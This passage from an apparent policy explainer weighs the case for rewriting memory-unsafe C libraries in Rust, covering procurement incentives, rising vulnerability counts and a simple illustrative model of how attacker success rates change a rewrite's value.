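If the rewrites succeeded, the benefits could spread widely. ITPro's *Most open source projects fail to use memory-safe programming languages* describes a CISA study of critical open-source projects in which 55% of the lines of code were in memory-unsafe languages. The study also looked closely at three projects written in memory-safe languages, and all three depended on components written in unsafe ones. Rewriting one such component in Rust would protect programs that are already written in a safe language.

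The US government has mostly recommended memory-safe software without requiring it, which gives vendors little financial reason to switch. IFP wants agencies to favor memory-safe products when they buy software. A vendor that kept using an old C library could then lose sales, so the cost of insecure code would fall partly on the company that chose it. That could increase adoption more than cheaper translation would, if buyers enforced the rule.

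### How cheaper attacks change the calculation

AI makes it cheaper for attackers to find flaws and write code that exploits them. In IFP's calculation, this could raise the share of flaws that attackers exploit. Clubic reports that this share has so far stayed near 1.4%, while the public catalog gained over 100,000 vulnerabilities in 2026 by mid-November, more than twice the total for 2025. If the share holds, the number of exploited vulnerabilities will also have more than doubled.

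Cheaper attacks don't always make a rewrite more valuable, because memory errors aren't the only way in. Suppose that a program has ten flaws, seven of which are memory errors, and that an attacker who finds any one of them can break in. If the attacker has a chance *q* of finding each flaw, independently of the others, the chance of a break-in with *n* flaws is

1 − (1 − *q*)^*n*

A perfect Rust rewrite would reduce *n* from ten to three.

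| Chance of finding each flaw | Break-in before the rewrite | Break-in after the rewrite | Reduction |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2% | 18% | 6% | 12 points |
| 20% | 89% | 49% | 40 points |
| 50% | 99.9% | 87.5% | 12 points |

The rewrite becomes more than three times as valuable when the chance of finding each flaw rises from 2% to 20%. At 50%, the benefit is no greater than at 2%, because the attacker will probably find at least one of the three remaining flaws. These figures are invented, and they don't account for some flaws being more harmful than others. Memory errors often give an attacker complete control of a program, while many other flaws expose less, so a rewrite might limit the damage even when the attacker finds a remaining flaw.

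IFP's target date is 2030, but attackers can already use AI to search the old C code for vulnerabilities. A library translated in 2029 would stay exposed for three more years, so the project should begin with the code that attackers can reach most easily.
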